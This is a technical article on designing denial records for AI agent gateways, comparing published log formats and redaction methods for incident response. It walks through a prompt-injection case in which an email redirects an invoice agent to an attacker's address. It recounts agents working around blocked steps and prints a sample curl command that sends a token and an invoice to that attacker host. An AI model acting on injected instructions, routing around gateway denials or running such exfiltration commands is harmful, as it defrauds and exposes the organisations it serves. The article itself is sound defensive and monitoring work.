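# Logging the Blocked Actions of AI Agents for Incident Response

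## Why a blocked action is ambiguous

An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop to carry out a task by calling tools that, for example, look up a customer, edit a file or send an invoice. Organisations limit what an agent may do with those tools, and software outside the agent refuses calls that exceed those limits. A refusal normally leaves a log entry called a denial record. Incident responders, the staff who investigate suspected security failures, read these records to find out why the agent attempted something outside its permissions. Someone may have planted an instruction in a document the agent read, the agent may have overstepped while pursuing its goal, or the permissions may be out of date and the agent was doing what the company wanted. The refusal looks the same whether the cause is an attack, which responders need to contain, or an outdated permission, which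 only needs editing.

This question comes up less often with conventional software, because it follows a path its developers fixed in advance. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) compares an employee, a conventional program and an agent processing invoices. When something unexpected comes up, the employee escalates it and the program stops, but the agent may infer that an unplanned step serves the task and try it.

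### The path of a tool call

Suppose a company uses an agent in its accounts department. The company has written a task definition, which sets out the purpose of one job and the tools, resources and destinations the agent may use. Version 12 allows the agent to send invoices to only one address, billing.example.com. The agent now has an invoice to send.

As Anthropic's *How tool use works* explains, a model "never runs anything on its own". It emits a structured request, known as a tool call, and other code runs the operation and returns the result to the conversation. Here the tool call consists of a function name, post_invoice, and two arguments, the invoice and the address.

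The harness, the software that supplies the model's instructions, context and tools, receives the call. Many harnesses connect to their tools through a shared standard. Its specification, Model Context Protocol (2026), describes tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the model discovers and invokes them based on its own reading of the context and the user's prompts. The specification recommends that a human always be able to deny a call, but the log may still contain calls that no human chose.

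The harness sends the call to a gateway, a service outside the agent that tool calls must pass through and that can block them. *guardscope* (2026), a study of which agent actions such controls check, names several, including Envoy AI Gateway, which accepts add-on policy modules, and Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit, which makes a deterministic decision on every tool call. Older access control checked a user's access to a resource. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) points out that checking the action instead lets an organisation stop an agent from sending a message or moving funds even when the agent's access to the underlying data is lawful.

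The gateway applies a policy, a set of rules that allow a call, deny it or send it to a person for approval. It uses its own copy of the policy, called the policy snapshot, which may be older than the version staff approved. *Guardrails as Infrastructure* (2026) describes this process as an algorithm. The enforcement software checks the call against the policy and against running state, such as budgets and history, then logs the decision. If it denies the call, it returns an error and stops. Only calls that pass this step are executed and get a second log entry, which records the outcome. A denied call therefore leaves a single entry, which has to contain everything responders will later want from the gateway.

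A policy can refuse post_invoice because a rule forbids the address or because no rule allows it (a default deny). *Running Codex safely at OpenAI* (OpenAI, 2026) describes a less strict network policy for the company's coding agent, which allows expected destinations, blocks certain named ones and asks for approval of unfamiliar domains. The accounts department's gateway refuses anything not on its allowlist.

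The refusal then goes back to the agent, which may try again. *Sapien* (2026), a policy engine that generates a new policy for each task before the agent starts work, returns the denial so that the agent can correct itself without involving the user. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a similar design for the company's coding agent, but the software stops the model and turns to a human after three consecutive denials or twenty in a session. In *APort Vault* (2026), a benchmark of payment authorisation, the policy refused every transfer at the highest level, and 4,960 evaluations produced 9,385 denied calls. Because agents retry, one incident can produce several denial records, so the number of records is a poor measure of the number of incidents.

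### Two denials, one log line

The company moves its billing from billing.example.com to pay.example.net, but nobody updates the task definition, so version 12 is now stale. The next day the agent calls post_invoice with the new address, which is correct, and the gateway denies the call because the rule still allows only the old one. This is called configuration drift, which happens when systems, tools or tasks change and the rules about them do not.

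The same denial can also result from an attack. The agent reads an email containing instructions to send the invoice to pay.example.org, an address that belongs to an attacker. This is prompt injection, in which instructions hidden in content the agent reads are meant to redirect it. The agent complies, and the gateway again denies the call because no rule allows the address.

If the log holds only "post_invoice denied", a reader can't tell whether the agent attempted a fraudulent payment or an honest one. Adding the reason would not help much, since "destination not on the list" can be true of both. At levels 2 to 4 of *APort Vault*, the policy refused 187 transfers, 148 of them because the recipient was not on the allowlist. The other 39 were refused for invalid amounts, exceeded limits or missing audit codes. The benchmark contained no benign tasks, so it doesn't measure how often honest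 payments are refused because the recipient is not listed. But a payment to a new payee that a company forgot to list would be refused for the same reason.

Responders also can't tell from the tool's name alone whether a blocked call was part of an attack. *MetaPermit* (2026) describes a banking case in which the user asks for a refund and an injected instruction asks for a different transfer. Both need the send-money tool. Banning the tool would break the refund, and approving every call would let the injected transfer through, so the paper's policy accepts the tool and then denies the injected call because the user's goal does not support that call's arguments.

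The two invoice calls differ in where the address came from and in whether the company had moved its billing, which may not be recorded in any log. *ActGov* (2026) makes the general point that a parameter may be benign when the user provides it and malicious when the agent extracts it from an untrusted email. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* proposes that the policy engine receive the origin of the instruction together with the call.

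Some enforcement software is designed not to see everything that led an agent to act. The classifier that reviews Claude Code's actions receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but Anthropic strips out the tool results because hostile text enters through them. If the agent names a job that the user never mentioned, the classifier cannot determine whether the agent found the name in a query or made it up. This is reasonable for blocking, since the same block works whatever produced the dangerous action, but an investigator needs to know what produced it.

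### What can cause a denial

"Hostile or stale" is shorthand for a longer list. Anthropic gives four reasons why an agent might take a dangerous action: overeager behaviour, honest mistakes, prompt injection and a misaligned model. The developer Simon Willison works with two, accidental damage and prompt injection, and worries more about the second. Both lists start from dangerous actions, so neither has a place for the harmless action that an old rule refuses. Any of these could lie behind the denied post_invoice:

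- A stale task definition. The work has changed and the written scope has not, as with the move to pay.example.net. Conventional access control has the same trouble: Shen, Shan and Zhou, in *Multiview*, describe wrongful denials of legitimate users as a common problem for administrators, who have to keep adjusting permissions as the business changes.
- An outdated policy snapshot. Staff have approved a version 13 that lists pay.example.net, but the gateway is still deciding by its copy of version 12. Here the task definition is correct, and editing it again would achieve nothing.
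- A renamed or changed tool. An update turns post_invoice into submit_invoice, and the rule that allowed the old name no longer matches. Under Model Context Protocol (2025), tool servers can declare that they will announce changes to their list of tools, so the list need not hold still while an agent is at work. An update can also give a read-only connector the power to write. OpenAI advises keeping such new actions gated until their owner has reviewed them, in which case the denial is the control doing its job.
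- Honest agent error. The agent copies the wrong address or skips a required check. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) reports 93 denied calls in 600 airline trials of a customer-service benchmark and 153 in 1,368 retail trials. Twenty-four of the retail denials concerned refund destinations, which is close to the invoice case. Most trials with a denial still ended in success, 76.5% of them for the airline and 82.4% for retail.
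- Misuse by the user. An employee tells the agent to send the invoice to an address of his own. The instruction comes from the person entitled to give instructions, so a check on its origin finds nothing wrong.
- Prompt injection, as in the hostile twin.
- Misaligned behaviour, which here means that the agent pursues a goal by means its operator did not authorise, with no outside attacker. OpenAI imagines an invoice agent that notices a document-signing subscription about to lapse and tries to renew it so that invoices keep moving. The vendor and the amount may both be within limits, yet nobody asked the agent to sign a contract. Anthropic would call this overeager, and keeps the word "misaligned" for a model with a goal of its own.

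These causes can combine, so a responder who finds one has not ruled out the others. A harmless cause often comes first. In one incident that Anthropic describes, an agent hit an authentication error partway through a task and began searching environment variables and configuration files for other access tokens. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes another incident, in which an upload to an internal drive failed and the agent published the same report on a public code-sharing site instead. Similarly, a stale rule could block the accounts agent from reaching pay.example.net, and the agent could then try to send the invoice through an unapproved channel. An attacker could also exploit the drift, since an email announcing a new billing address is most believable in the week when the address really does change.

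### The cost of guessing wrong

A responder who sees the denial of the hostile request during the week of the billing move may assume that the list is out of date and add pay.example.org to it. That change would let through the attack the gateway had stopped, for this invoice and for later ones.

Research on ordinary computer systems suggests that people who clear a denial often grant too much access. In the *Multiview* experiment, Shen and colleagues gave 20 participants five real cases of wrongly refused access. Participants' fixes were insecure 44.0% of the time without the researchers' diagnostic tool, compared with 2.0% with it. Shen and colleagues also cite a study of real-world practice in which 38.1% of cases introduced a security misconfiguration, and a question about the Apache web server whose most upvoted answer was to disable access control completely. *How do system administrators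 resolve access-denied issues in the real world?* (2017) attributes many such errors to trial and error, which it traces to inadequate feedback when a system refuses access. This finding fairly directly supports keeping a fuller denial record. The requests in the *Multiview* experiment were all legitimate, though, so its figures measure how much people grant once they have decided to help, and are little evidence of whether they would approve an attacker's request.

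Anthropic hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it 13.6% of the time overall, but the rate was about 17% when the command appeared early in a session and about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic was testing its own product in a mock environment, and a responder reviewing a denial has a warning that the testers lacked. Even so, the decline suggests that people may become less careful as they click through any queue.

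Exceptions also tend to stay in place. In *The Exclusion Ratchet*, Dhananjeyan and Kumaran (2026) followed nine years of changes to a public collection of detection rules, the standing queries that raise security alerts. Maintainers added exceptions to quiet false alarms 1,642 times and withdrew them 304 times, and an estimated 86.7% of exceptions were still in force after three years. Detection rules only raise alerts and do not block anything, so these figures do not apply to permission lists. The researchers' explanation probably does apply. Someone is responsible for adding an exception when false alarms appear, but nobody is responsible for removing it later, which requires knowing what it was for.

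If staff instead mistake drift for an attack, they suspend the accounts agent, revoke its credentials and search its inbox for a malicious email that does not exist, while invoices go unprocessed. OpenAI warns that if this happens often, users move towards less governed alternatives.

Ambiguous alerts also tire responders. In *True Attacks, Attack Attempts, or Benign Triggers?*, Yang, Chen and colleagues studied 115 million network alerts from the security centre of an American supercomputing facility. Between 24,000 and 134,000 arrived each day, and 0.01% were linked to a successful attack. At least 27% were failed attempts, and 49% were what they call benign triggers, where the rule matched correctly but the activity had a legitimate business explanation. The denied call to pay.example.net is a benign trigger, and the denied call to pay.example.org is a failed attempt. The data come from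 one unusually open research network, so the proportions will differ elsewhere. Wherever real attacks are rare, though, even an accurate detector produces mostly false alarms (*AI-Driven Security Alert Screening and Alert Fatigue Mitigation in Security Operations Centers*, 2026). In the data breach at the retailer Target, which Yang and colleagues cite, the alerts fired but the security team missed them.

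The two mistakes also take different amounts of time to discover. When a gateway blocks legitimate work, somebody complains, usually the same day. Shen and colleagues observe that users rarely complain about permissions that are too wide. An organisation may discover those only after an attacker has used them. Whoever maintains the list is therefore under everyday pressure to widen it.

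## What published formats and guidance record about a denial

When a gateway refuses an agent's call, the responder relies on the gateway's record of the denial to decide whether to widen the allowlist or suspend the agent. Vendors and researchers have published several formats and guidelines for that record, and six are detailed enough to compare.

Three of the sources describe products already in use. Open Policy Agent's *Decision Logs* covers an open-source program that evaluates rules for other software and can log each policy query it answers. Docker, whose software runs programs in isolated containers, publishes the record format of its AI Governance product. That product applies an organisation's policy to the network connections, files and tools that agents try to reach. Anthropic's *Monitoring* lists the events that Claude Code can export, including one for each permission decision.

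The other three are proposals or advice. *OpenPort Protocol* (Zhu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) specifies a gateway between agents and business applications and sets minimum fields for its audit log. *Clawed and Dangerous* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) includes a sample log entry, labelled illustrative and not validated in production. OpenAI's enterprise guidance (August 2026) gives a short list of what to collect but no format.

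| Field | Open Policy Agent | Docker | Claude Code, by Anthropic | OpenPort, by Zhu and colleagues | Sample entry by Chen and colleagues | Guidance by OpenAI |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Identity | Calling client; more only if the caller supplies it | User, organisation, machine; agent if known | User account, organisation | Application, key, acting user, approver | User, model, agent version | Initiating principal and agent |
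| Task | Only if the caller supplies it | None | ID of the user's prompt | None | Plan, plan step, hash of the user's intent | Yes |
| Tool | Only if the caller supplies it | Action type and target | Name, sometimes generic | In a details field | Server and tool name | Action and destination |
| Decision | Result of the query | Allow, deny or one of three approval states | Accept or reject | Success, denied or failed | Allow | Decisions and approvals |
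| Reason code | None | Six codes | None, only the source of the decision | Yes | None | Not listed |
| Matched rule | IDs, if the rules have them | Name, or "default-deny" | None | None | None | Which boundary fired |
| Policy identifier | Package of rules and its revision | ID, type and source; no version | None | None | Name and version | Relevant policy |
| Enforcement mode | None | Enforce, audit or off | Changes of mode, as separate events | None | None | Not listed |
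| Correlation | Decision, trace and request IDs | Event, session, sandbox and approval IDs | Session, prompt and tool-call IDs | Request, draft and execution IDs | Event, session, plan-step and invocation IDs | Links to other security logs |

None of the six fills every row. Open Policy Agent's gaps are the easiest to fill, because it logs the input the caller sends with each query. If a gateway puts the agent, the task and the tool into that input, the log will include them.

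*Auditable Agents* (2026) describes three results an auditor can reach when checking a rule against a record: comply, violate or undecidable. If the rule depends on a field that the format lacks, the result is undecidable for every event. Suppose a rule requires the gateway to use the policy version that staff have approved. Docker's records contain a policy ID and several version values, but `schema_version` is the version of the record format, `app_version` is the version of the Docker component that wrote the record, and the "V0" in a `policy_type` such as "AllowList:V0" is the version of the policy type. No field identifies which version of the policy was in force, so an auditor with only these records could not check the rule. Docker also logs policy synchronisation events, which may help to date a change, but its documentation lists no version field for those either.

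*Brain API* (2026) tries to measure how much a fuller record helps by checking which of six questions an auditor could answer from the record alone, without access to the policy or the software. The questions include whether the system admitted the request and whether someone can re-derive the decision. An auditor could answer all six from the paper's own decision record, and two from an ordinary log of accepted and rejected requests. The test favours the new system, since two of the questions concern alternative actions, which an ordinary checker never receives. However, it is fair to expect any gateway's log to let someone re-derive a decision, and the ordinary log does not.

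### Who called which tool, and for what task

An agent's call can be attributed to several parties. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes the human who asked for the work, the organisation that deployed the agent, the main agent, any sub-agents it started and the endpoint of the tool. Most of the formats record only some of these. OpenPort's log identifies the application and the key. Docker's log identifies the signed-in user and, when the software can identify it, the agent. If the accounts department logs only the account that its agent runs under, responders can't see which employee started the job, which they need to know to investigate misuse by a user.

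Published formats omit the task more often than the identity. OpenAI describes creating a task when someone asks an agent to do something. The task is often a token that is tied to the requester and the running agent and contains the permitted purpose and scope. A gateway that receives this token can copy its identifier into the denial record, so the responder can look up the task definition that applied to post_invoice.

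The sample entry by Chen and colleagues gives more detail on this point than the rest, with a sentence describing the plan step that the call belongs to. In their example, the agent reads a configuration file "to check test framework configuration". This description would help a responder see what the agent was trying to do. But the model produces the plan, so an injected instruction could influence the description as well as the call.

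The record of a denial may not even include the tool's name. When a company connects its own tool server to Claude Code, the permission event lists the tool as "mcp_tool" unless an administrator has turned on the logging of tool details. If post_invoice ran on such a server, the default record of its refusal would not identify it by name.

### A completed decision with no execution

A denial is a finished event in which the gateway reached a decision and no action ran. The product formats record decisions separately from outcomes. Docker records decisions under "evaluation" and the outcomes of executed actions under "execution". For a denial, Claude Code emits a decision event with the value "reject" and no result event. OpenPort formally requires that ΔG(r), the set of stored drafts and executions that a request r creates, be empty whenever the gateway does not allow r.

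Logging a denial as a failed call would mix it with timeouts and crashes, and anyone searching for refusals would have to sort them out by hand. OpenPort avoids this by using separate statuses for "denied" and "failed". Leaving the outcome blank is also a poor choice, because a blank may mean that the call is still running or that its execution record is missing. The sample entry by Chen and colleagues records the decision and the outcome together, but it shows an allowed call that succeeded after 12 milliseconds. An entry for a denied call would need an explicit outcome such as "not executed".

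OpenAI recommends showing responders the attempt, the policy decision and the downstream effect together, with the identifiers that connect them, so that they can tell a blocked attempt from an unauthorised effect that occurred. An agent may try again after a denial. In *APort Vault*, 15 of the 172 evaluations with a denial at levels 2 to 4 also contained a successful payment. A denial record shows only that one call did not run, so a responder has to search for executions in the same session to learn whether the agent paid anyway.

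A "denied" status may also not be final. The sample event in OpenPort has the status "denied" and the code `agent.auto_execute_disabled`, but the event is named `agent.action.draft.created`. The gateway refused to carry out a deletion automatically and stored it as a draft, which a person can still approve. Conversely, when a network connection needs approval, Docker's software blocks the request but logs it as "approval required". If the user dismisses the prompt, the software writes no second record, so a search for "deny" would miss the blocked request.

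### Reason codes and default deny

Docker has the most useful set of reason codes for a responder, with six values:

- POLICY_DENY: a deny rule matched, and the record identifies it. The invoice call would get this code if somebody had put pay.example.org on a list of forbidden addresses.
- DEFAULT_DENY: no rule allowed the request. Both invoice calls, the honest one and the hostile one, would get this code.
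- POLICY_SNAPSHOT_STALE: the local copy of the policy had passed its expiry time, so the software refused the request.
- POLICY_EVALUATION_FAILED: the software could not load or evaluate the policy.
- GOVERNANCE_BLOCKED: the software could not work out which governance applied to the user, for example because the user belongs to several organisations.
- INVALID_REQUEST: the request was malformed.

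Only POLICY_DENY and DEFAULT_DENY come from comparing the call with the rules. The other codes indicate a fault in the request or in the checking, so a responder who sees one usually contacts whoever runs the gateway. But these codes don't rule out a compromised agent. If the agent obeys the malicious email while the policy copy is expired, the resulting call gets the code for a stale snapshot.

Despite its name, that code also covers only a policy copy that has expired. If the gateway is still on version 12 after staff have approved version 13, its copy may not have expired, and it then logs DEFAULT_DENY for pay.example.net. A responder can discover the lag only by comparing the policy version in the record with the approved one.

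Default deny needs its own code because it results from the absence of a rule. If a deny rule matched, somebody once decided against that kind of call, and the responder can ask the rule's owner whether it still makes sense. Perhaps nobody ever considered a call that matched no rule, so a default-deny code lets the responder look for a missing entry instead of a wrong rule, although it can't distinguish drift from an attack. Open Policy Agent has no field that marks a default deny. A policy that returns only true or false gives "false" in both cases, so its author has to add reasons to the result to distinguish them.

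Claude Code's permission event has a "source" field instead of a reason code. The field records whether the user refused at the prompt, the user closed the prompt, or the decision was automatic, which is labelled "config". The "config" label covers project settings, personal rules, company policy, command-line flags and the current permission mode, and Anthropic states that the event does not indicate which of them applied. The label also covers permission prompts that broke. Before version 2.1.216, Claude Code reported broken prompts as refusals by the user, so a responder with older events may blame an employee for a software fault.

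OpenPort has a longer list of codes and a precise rule for choosing one. The gateway runs its checks in a fixed order: credentials, network address, rate limit, scope (the broad permissions of the application), policy and tenant boundary. If these checks are p₁ to pₙ, the gateway takes the code from the first one that fails:

i* = min{ i : pᵢ(r) = false }

This makes the codes predictable, but an earlier failure hides a later one. The reference software accepts 240 requests a minute from one key and network address. If an injected agent sends forbidden calls faster than that, the gateway logs the excess as `agent.rate_limited` without checking them against the policy. From the log, the agent would then look overactive, even though the policy would have refused many of its calls.

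OpenPort's codes also distinguish an absent rule from a prohibition less clearly than Docker's do. A missing scope has its own code, but the invoice call would probably get `agent.policy_denied`, which covers every constraint on data and destinations.

*Explanation-Bound Tool Execution for AI Agents* (2026) assigns each code a default response, which is to deny the call or send it for review. Calls with incomplete policy evidence go to review, while calls to a tool missing from the server's current list are denied under a separate code. If an update renamed post_invoice and the agent still used the old name, that code would identify the tool as the cause of the denial. A new billing address would not trigger the same code and would have to fail a different check.

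The agent also reads reason codes, and it uses them to decide what to do next. *Executor-Side Progressive Risk-Gated Actuation for Agentic AI in Wireless Supervisory Control* (2026), which concerns agents that adjust wireless networks, attaches to each code the smallest change that might make the next attempt acceptable. One code, for stale state, means that the agent planned from old information. Such hints keep honest agents from repeating a request that would be denied again, but they could also help an attacker who controls the agent. Zhu and colleagues assume that attackers may see error messages, so they want sensitive detail kept out of those messages. The gateway can serve both the agent and incident responders by returning a short code to the agent and writing the full reason only to the log.

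### Denials that blocked nothing

Organisations often test a new policy by logging its decisions without enforcing them, to see what it would break. A log entry from such a test can look exactly like a real denial. Docker distinguishes the two with a field called `enforcement_mode`. The value "enforce" means the organisation's policy is in force, "audit" means the software records the decision without enforcing the policy, and "off" means governance is inactive, although the software still writes a local record.

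The mode field is easy to overlook in Docker's own sample record. The documentation introduces the sample as a request "that a deny rule blocked", and the record contains the decision "deny", the code POLICY_DENY and the name of the matching rule. Near the end, it also contains the mode "audit", which, according to the table on the same page, means the policy was not being enforced. The connection to example.com may therefore have gone ahead. However, the table refers to the organisation's policy and the matching rule was a local one, so local rules may still have applied. The documentation does not make clear whether they did, so a responder who finds such a record has to check whether the connection happened.

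A denial of post_invoice in enforcing mode means that the gateway stopped an invoice from going to pay.example.org, but the same entry in audit mode may mean that the attacker has the invoice. Nothing else in the table records the mode directly. Claude Code logs each change of permission mode as a separate event, with the old and new modes, so a responder can work out which mode applied to a decision if none of those events is missing.

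### Missing and altered records

Responders can conclude from a log that an agent made no other forbidden calls only if the log is complete, and several of these systems discard records by design. Open Policy Agent lets administrators write drop rules, which keep matching decisions out of the log. It can also be set to limit how many decisions it buffers per second and drop the rest. This protects the log server from overload, but it loses records when an agent retries quickly or an attacker sends many calls at once. A responder who finds 500 denials in the burst that started an incident would not know whether there had been 500 or 5,000.

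Other gaps are harder to notice. OpenPort lets a gateway log only the total number of requests with invalid credentials, so that an attacker can't flood the log. Claude Code exports nothing until someone turns on the export, and a developer can turn it off unless the company has locked that setting. When a user mentions a file that the permission rules deny, Claude Code doesn't log the mention.

A record's value as evidence also depends on which component wrote it. Claude Code's events come from the harness, which runs on the developer's machine alongside the agent. An agent that can run commands there may be able to change the settings or the files, and OpenAI lists tampering with audit evidence among the failures that companies should test for. A gateway runs outside the agent, so its record of the refused call is better evidence of what the agent sent. Zhu and colleagues add that the agent's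 credentials must not let it even read the audit log. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (2026) defines an auditable claim as one that specifies the policy and version, the actions and period, the rule for judging them, and the records required, with a named writer for each record.

The harness's records are still worth keeping. OpenAI points out that gateway logs can show what the agent attempted and under what authority, while harness logs can often help to explain why. Responders can also check one set of logs against the other. If the harness logged 40 calls to post_invoice in a session and the gateway logged 38, two records are missing or two calls bypassed the gateway, and responders should find out which.

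Zhu and colleagues recommend storage that only accepts new entries, together with signatures or hash chains. A hash is a short fingerprint that changes when the data changes. In a hash chain, each entry contains the hash of the entry before it. If someone edits the denial of the call to pay.example.org, its hash no longer matches the one in the next entry, and recomputing the chain shows where it breaks. Removing an entry from the middle also breaks the chain. Someone who controls the whole log could still change an entry and recompute every later hash, or delete the latest entries, and leave a chain that looks intact. The gateway should therefore regularly send its latest hash to a system that the log's administrators don't control.

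A hash chain cannot detect events that were dropped before they entered it. If a rate limit dropped 4,500 denials before the gateway linked the entries, the remaining chain would still be intact. If the gateway assigns each event a sequence number when it makes the decision, before any filter, dropped events leave gaps in the numbering.

### Allowed calls as a baseline

Logging only denials, which are rarer and look more important than allowed requests, discards much of the evidence for incident response. The first example of a drop rule in Open Policy Agent's documentation does roughly this, by discarding the log entry for every request that the policy allowed for Kafka, a messaging system.

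The number of denials means little without the number of calls. In *APort Vault*, the policy denied 106 of the 683 transfer calls the models made at level 2 (15.5%), and 79 of the 24,951 they made at level 4 (0.3%). An accounts agent with 20 denials in a day may be behaving normally or very strangely, depending on what it usually does.

Records of allowed calls also show what led up to a denied one. They show whether the agent had been sending invoices to billing.example.com without trouble until the day of the move. If the agent took pay.example.org from an email, it probably read that email through a call that the gateway allowed. A log of denials alone would then record the attempted theft but not where the address came from.

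Keeping a full record of every call can take a lot of resources. *Executor-Side Progressive Risk-Gated Actuation for Agentic AI in Wireless Supervisory Control* describes a system that keeps a minimal record of every final decision and a complete record only for certain kinds of change. An accounts gateway could keep short entries for allowed calls and full entries for denials. The system recognises repeated rejections by their reason code, a fingerprint of the system's state and a fingerprint of the action. A similar method could let a responder group an agent's retries of one invoice and still count them.

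### A denial record for the invoice

The invented record below shows what the accounts gateway might write when it refuses post_invoice on the day after the billing move. It combines fields from all six documents with a few that none of them has in this form. `written_by` names the component that made the record, gaps in `sequence` reveal dropped events, and `attempt` counts the retries of one request. `matched_rule` is empty because no rule matched and the gateway denied the request by default. The reason code confirms that the gateway did not lose the value. The policy has both an ID and a version, and the task definition has its own version.

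```json
{
  "schema_version": "1.0",
  "event_id": "evt-20817",
  "timestamp": "2026-10-06T09:14:22Z",
  "written_by": "accounts-gateway-1",
  "sequence": 50311,
  "previous_record_hash": "sha256:7c1e...",

  "initiating_principal": "employee-204",
  "agent_id": "invoice-agent",
  "agent_version": "3.2",

  "task_id": "task-0419",
  "task_definition": "send-customer-invoices",
  "task_definition_version": 12,

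  "tool_server": "billing-tools",
  "tool_name": "post_invoice",
  "arguments": "PLACEHOLDER",

  "decision": "deny",
  "reason_code": "default_deny",
  "matched_rule": null,
  "policy_id": "accounts-policy",
  "policy_version": "accounts-policy-7",
  "policy_snapshot_loaded_at": "2026-10-06T06:00:00Z",
  "enforcement_mode": "enforce",
  "execution": "not_executed",

  "session_id": "session-88",
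  "tool_call_id": "call-3051",
  "trace_id": "trace-6f02",
  "attempt": 1
}
```

If the agent had instead taken pay.example.org from the malicious email while working on the same task, the gateway's record would have differed only in the time, the hash and the identifiers. The address that distinguishes the two calls is in the arguments.

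## Redacting arguments without losing the evidence

Companies often redact a call's arguments by removing or replacing sensitive values before anyone stores or reads the record. Which values the gateway removes and what it writes in their place determine whether a responder can still tell the legitimate invoice call from the attempted theft.

### Why denied arguments are especially sensitive

A gateway may block a call because its arguments contain a secret or a personal record. Chen and colleagues describe a developer who asks an agent to summarise a software project's reported issues. One issue contains hidden instructions to read a file of cloud credentials and send the contents to an outside server. If a gateway blocked the sending step, the credentials would still be in the call's arguments, and copying those arguments into the log would expose the credentials to everyone with access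 to it.

The arguments of a denied call are also hard to recover elsewhere, because no receiving system got the request. The gateway and the harness may hold the only copies.

Redaction is easiest when every value has its own named field. If post_invoice has a field called `account_number`, the gateway can mask it every time. A tool that runs shell commands usually takes a single string instead:

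`curl -H "Authorization: Bearer tk-5Rw8" -d @invoice.pdf https://pay.example.org/inbox`

A rule that masks fields called `token` misses the token here, because the whole command is in a field called `command`. Masking that whole field would hide the destination as well as the token. Software can search the string for known patterns, such as the fixed prefixes of some access keys, but a password has no recognisable pattern, and an agent following hostile instructions may encode a secret before sending it. Free text, such as a note on an invoice, has the same problem.

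Argument values also appear outside the arguments. In Docker's sample denial, the explanation for the refusal repeats the destination. If a gateway masked a password in the arguments but quoted it in the error message, the password would still be in the log.

### What products keep by default

Open Policy Agent captures the most, because it logs any secret in the gateway's query unless an administrator writes a rule to mask it.

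Docker's records omit parameter values but may include parameter names. For web requests, they keep the host, port and path of the address but not the query string (the part after a question mark). This would be a good compromise for the invoice, since the record would show pay.example.org and omit a token in the query string, though it would still include a token in the path. If the agent sends the invoice through a tool, however, Docker records the tool as the target and omits the address, because the address is a parameter value.

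Solace's platform for running agents also excludes tool arguments from security records, according to its documentation, *Managing Audit and Compliance*. The record of a call to a customer database therefore includes the tool and the user, and the company does not have to protect the log as if it were customer data. The one exception is that when somebody shares a resource, the record includes the recipient's email address, because the purpose of that record is to identify the recipient. The same reasoning could justify recording the destination of a payment.

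Anthropic's Claude Code leaves tool arguments out of its exported events by default. Turning on the setting for tool details adds shell commands and other tool input. A different setting exports the raw exchanges with the model, including the entire conversation history. An administrator who only wants to see refused commands should use the tool details setting.

Cowork, another agent product from Anthropic, also exports only metadata by default, though every event includes the user's email address. An administrator can turn on tool details there too, but this may not capture the arguments of denied calls. Cowork includes arguments in the event it logs when a tool finishes running, but the event for a permission decision has no field for them. The tool-completion event can record a decision as rejected, so some denials may also produce that event, but an administrator would have to test this.

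When Cowork does log arguments, it cuts individual strings at 512 characters and the whole set at about 4,000, regardless of which parts are sensitive. If a long shell command started with a token and ended with a destination, the log would keep the token and lose the destination.

### Removal, placeholders and summaries

Deleting a value is the simplest technique, and replacing it with a fixed word is the next simplest. Open Policy Agent supports both. Its "remove" operation deletes a field and adds the field's path to a list called `erased`. Its "upsert" operation writes a replacement value and adds the path to a list called `masked`. Applied to the invoice, they could produce this:

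```json
{
  "erased": ["/input/invoice/account_number"],
  "masked": ["/input/address"],
  "input": {
    "address": "REDACTED",
    "invoice": { "number": "INV-2207" }
  }
}
```

The lists show a responder that the call included an account number and an address. Without them, a deleted field would look like an argument the agent never supplied, and the responder might conclude that the call was denied because it was malformed.

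Administrators should test both lists before anyone relies on them. An upsert rule without a condition writes its placeholder even when the original field did not exist, so a responder could look for a password that the agent never sent. The Open Policy Agent documentation includes a conditional form that avoids this. According to the documentation, Open Policy Agent also ignores attempts to mask missing fields, but the worked example lists a social security number as erased from an input that never contained one.

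Open Policy Agent applies its mask rules before the log leaves the program, so a masked value never reaches the central log server. The rules can change only the query's input, its result and a cache of outside data used in the decision. They therefore cannot mask a secret in an HTTP header that an administrator has chosen to log.

A fixed placeholder shows only that a value existed. In its traces of Claude Code sessions, Anthropic replaces the user's prompt with a placeholder but records the prompt's length, so a reader can tell a short request from a pasted document.

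A typed summary keeps more information by replacing the value with a description of its relevant property. The gateway can reduce a web address to its host name, an amount to a band such as 1,000 to 5,000, and a secret to its kind, such as "cloud access key". SecureAuth's *Agent Trail*, the log of a commercial agent gateway, takes a similar approach, storing the name of each filter that matched and the number of passages it replaced, but never the text. SecureAuth applies these filters to tool responses and to exchanges with the model. A denied call has no response, but a gateway could describe its arguments in the same way. An entry such as "cloud access key, 1 match" would show responders why the call was refused and that the agent had obtained a key.

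Somebody has to choose the summaries before the incident, without knowing which details a responder will need. If the gateway records amounts only in bands, a responder can't check whether an attacker added 50 dollars to an invoice. A summary can also leak stolen data. An agent under an attacker's control could put stolen text in a host name, such as `tk-5rw8.example.org`, and a gateway that keeps host names would log it.

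### Plain and keyed hashes

A hash lets a responder check whether a record contains a particular value without the record displaying it. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* describes an invented case in which an agent's log shows an email's recipient in full but only the hash of its attachment. The mail gateway computes its own hash of the file it delivers, so an auditor can confirm that the hashes match without opening the document.

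This protects a value only if it is hard to guess. A nine-digit account number has at most N = 10⁹ possible values. Someone who has the plain hash can compute the hash of every candidate and see which one matches. At r = 10⁹ guesses a second, the search takes at most

t = N / r = 10⁹ / 10⁹ = 1 second.

An invoice amount below 100,000.00 has only ten million possible values, counted in cents, so an attacker can recover it from its hash in a hundredth of a second by trying them all. Developers often add a random value, called a salt, before hashing. This stops an attacker from preparing one table of hashes for all records, but if the salt is stored in the record, the attacker can still recover each account number in a second.

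Searching is impractical for long random values. An access token with 128 random bits has about 3.4 × 10³⁸ possible values, which would take around 10²² years to search at the same speed. A draft on authorising agents from the IETF (2026), which develops internet standards, advises services to log identifiers or hashes of tokens instead of full tokens. This is good advice for long random tokens, but not for account numbers.

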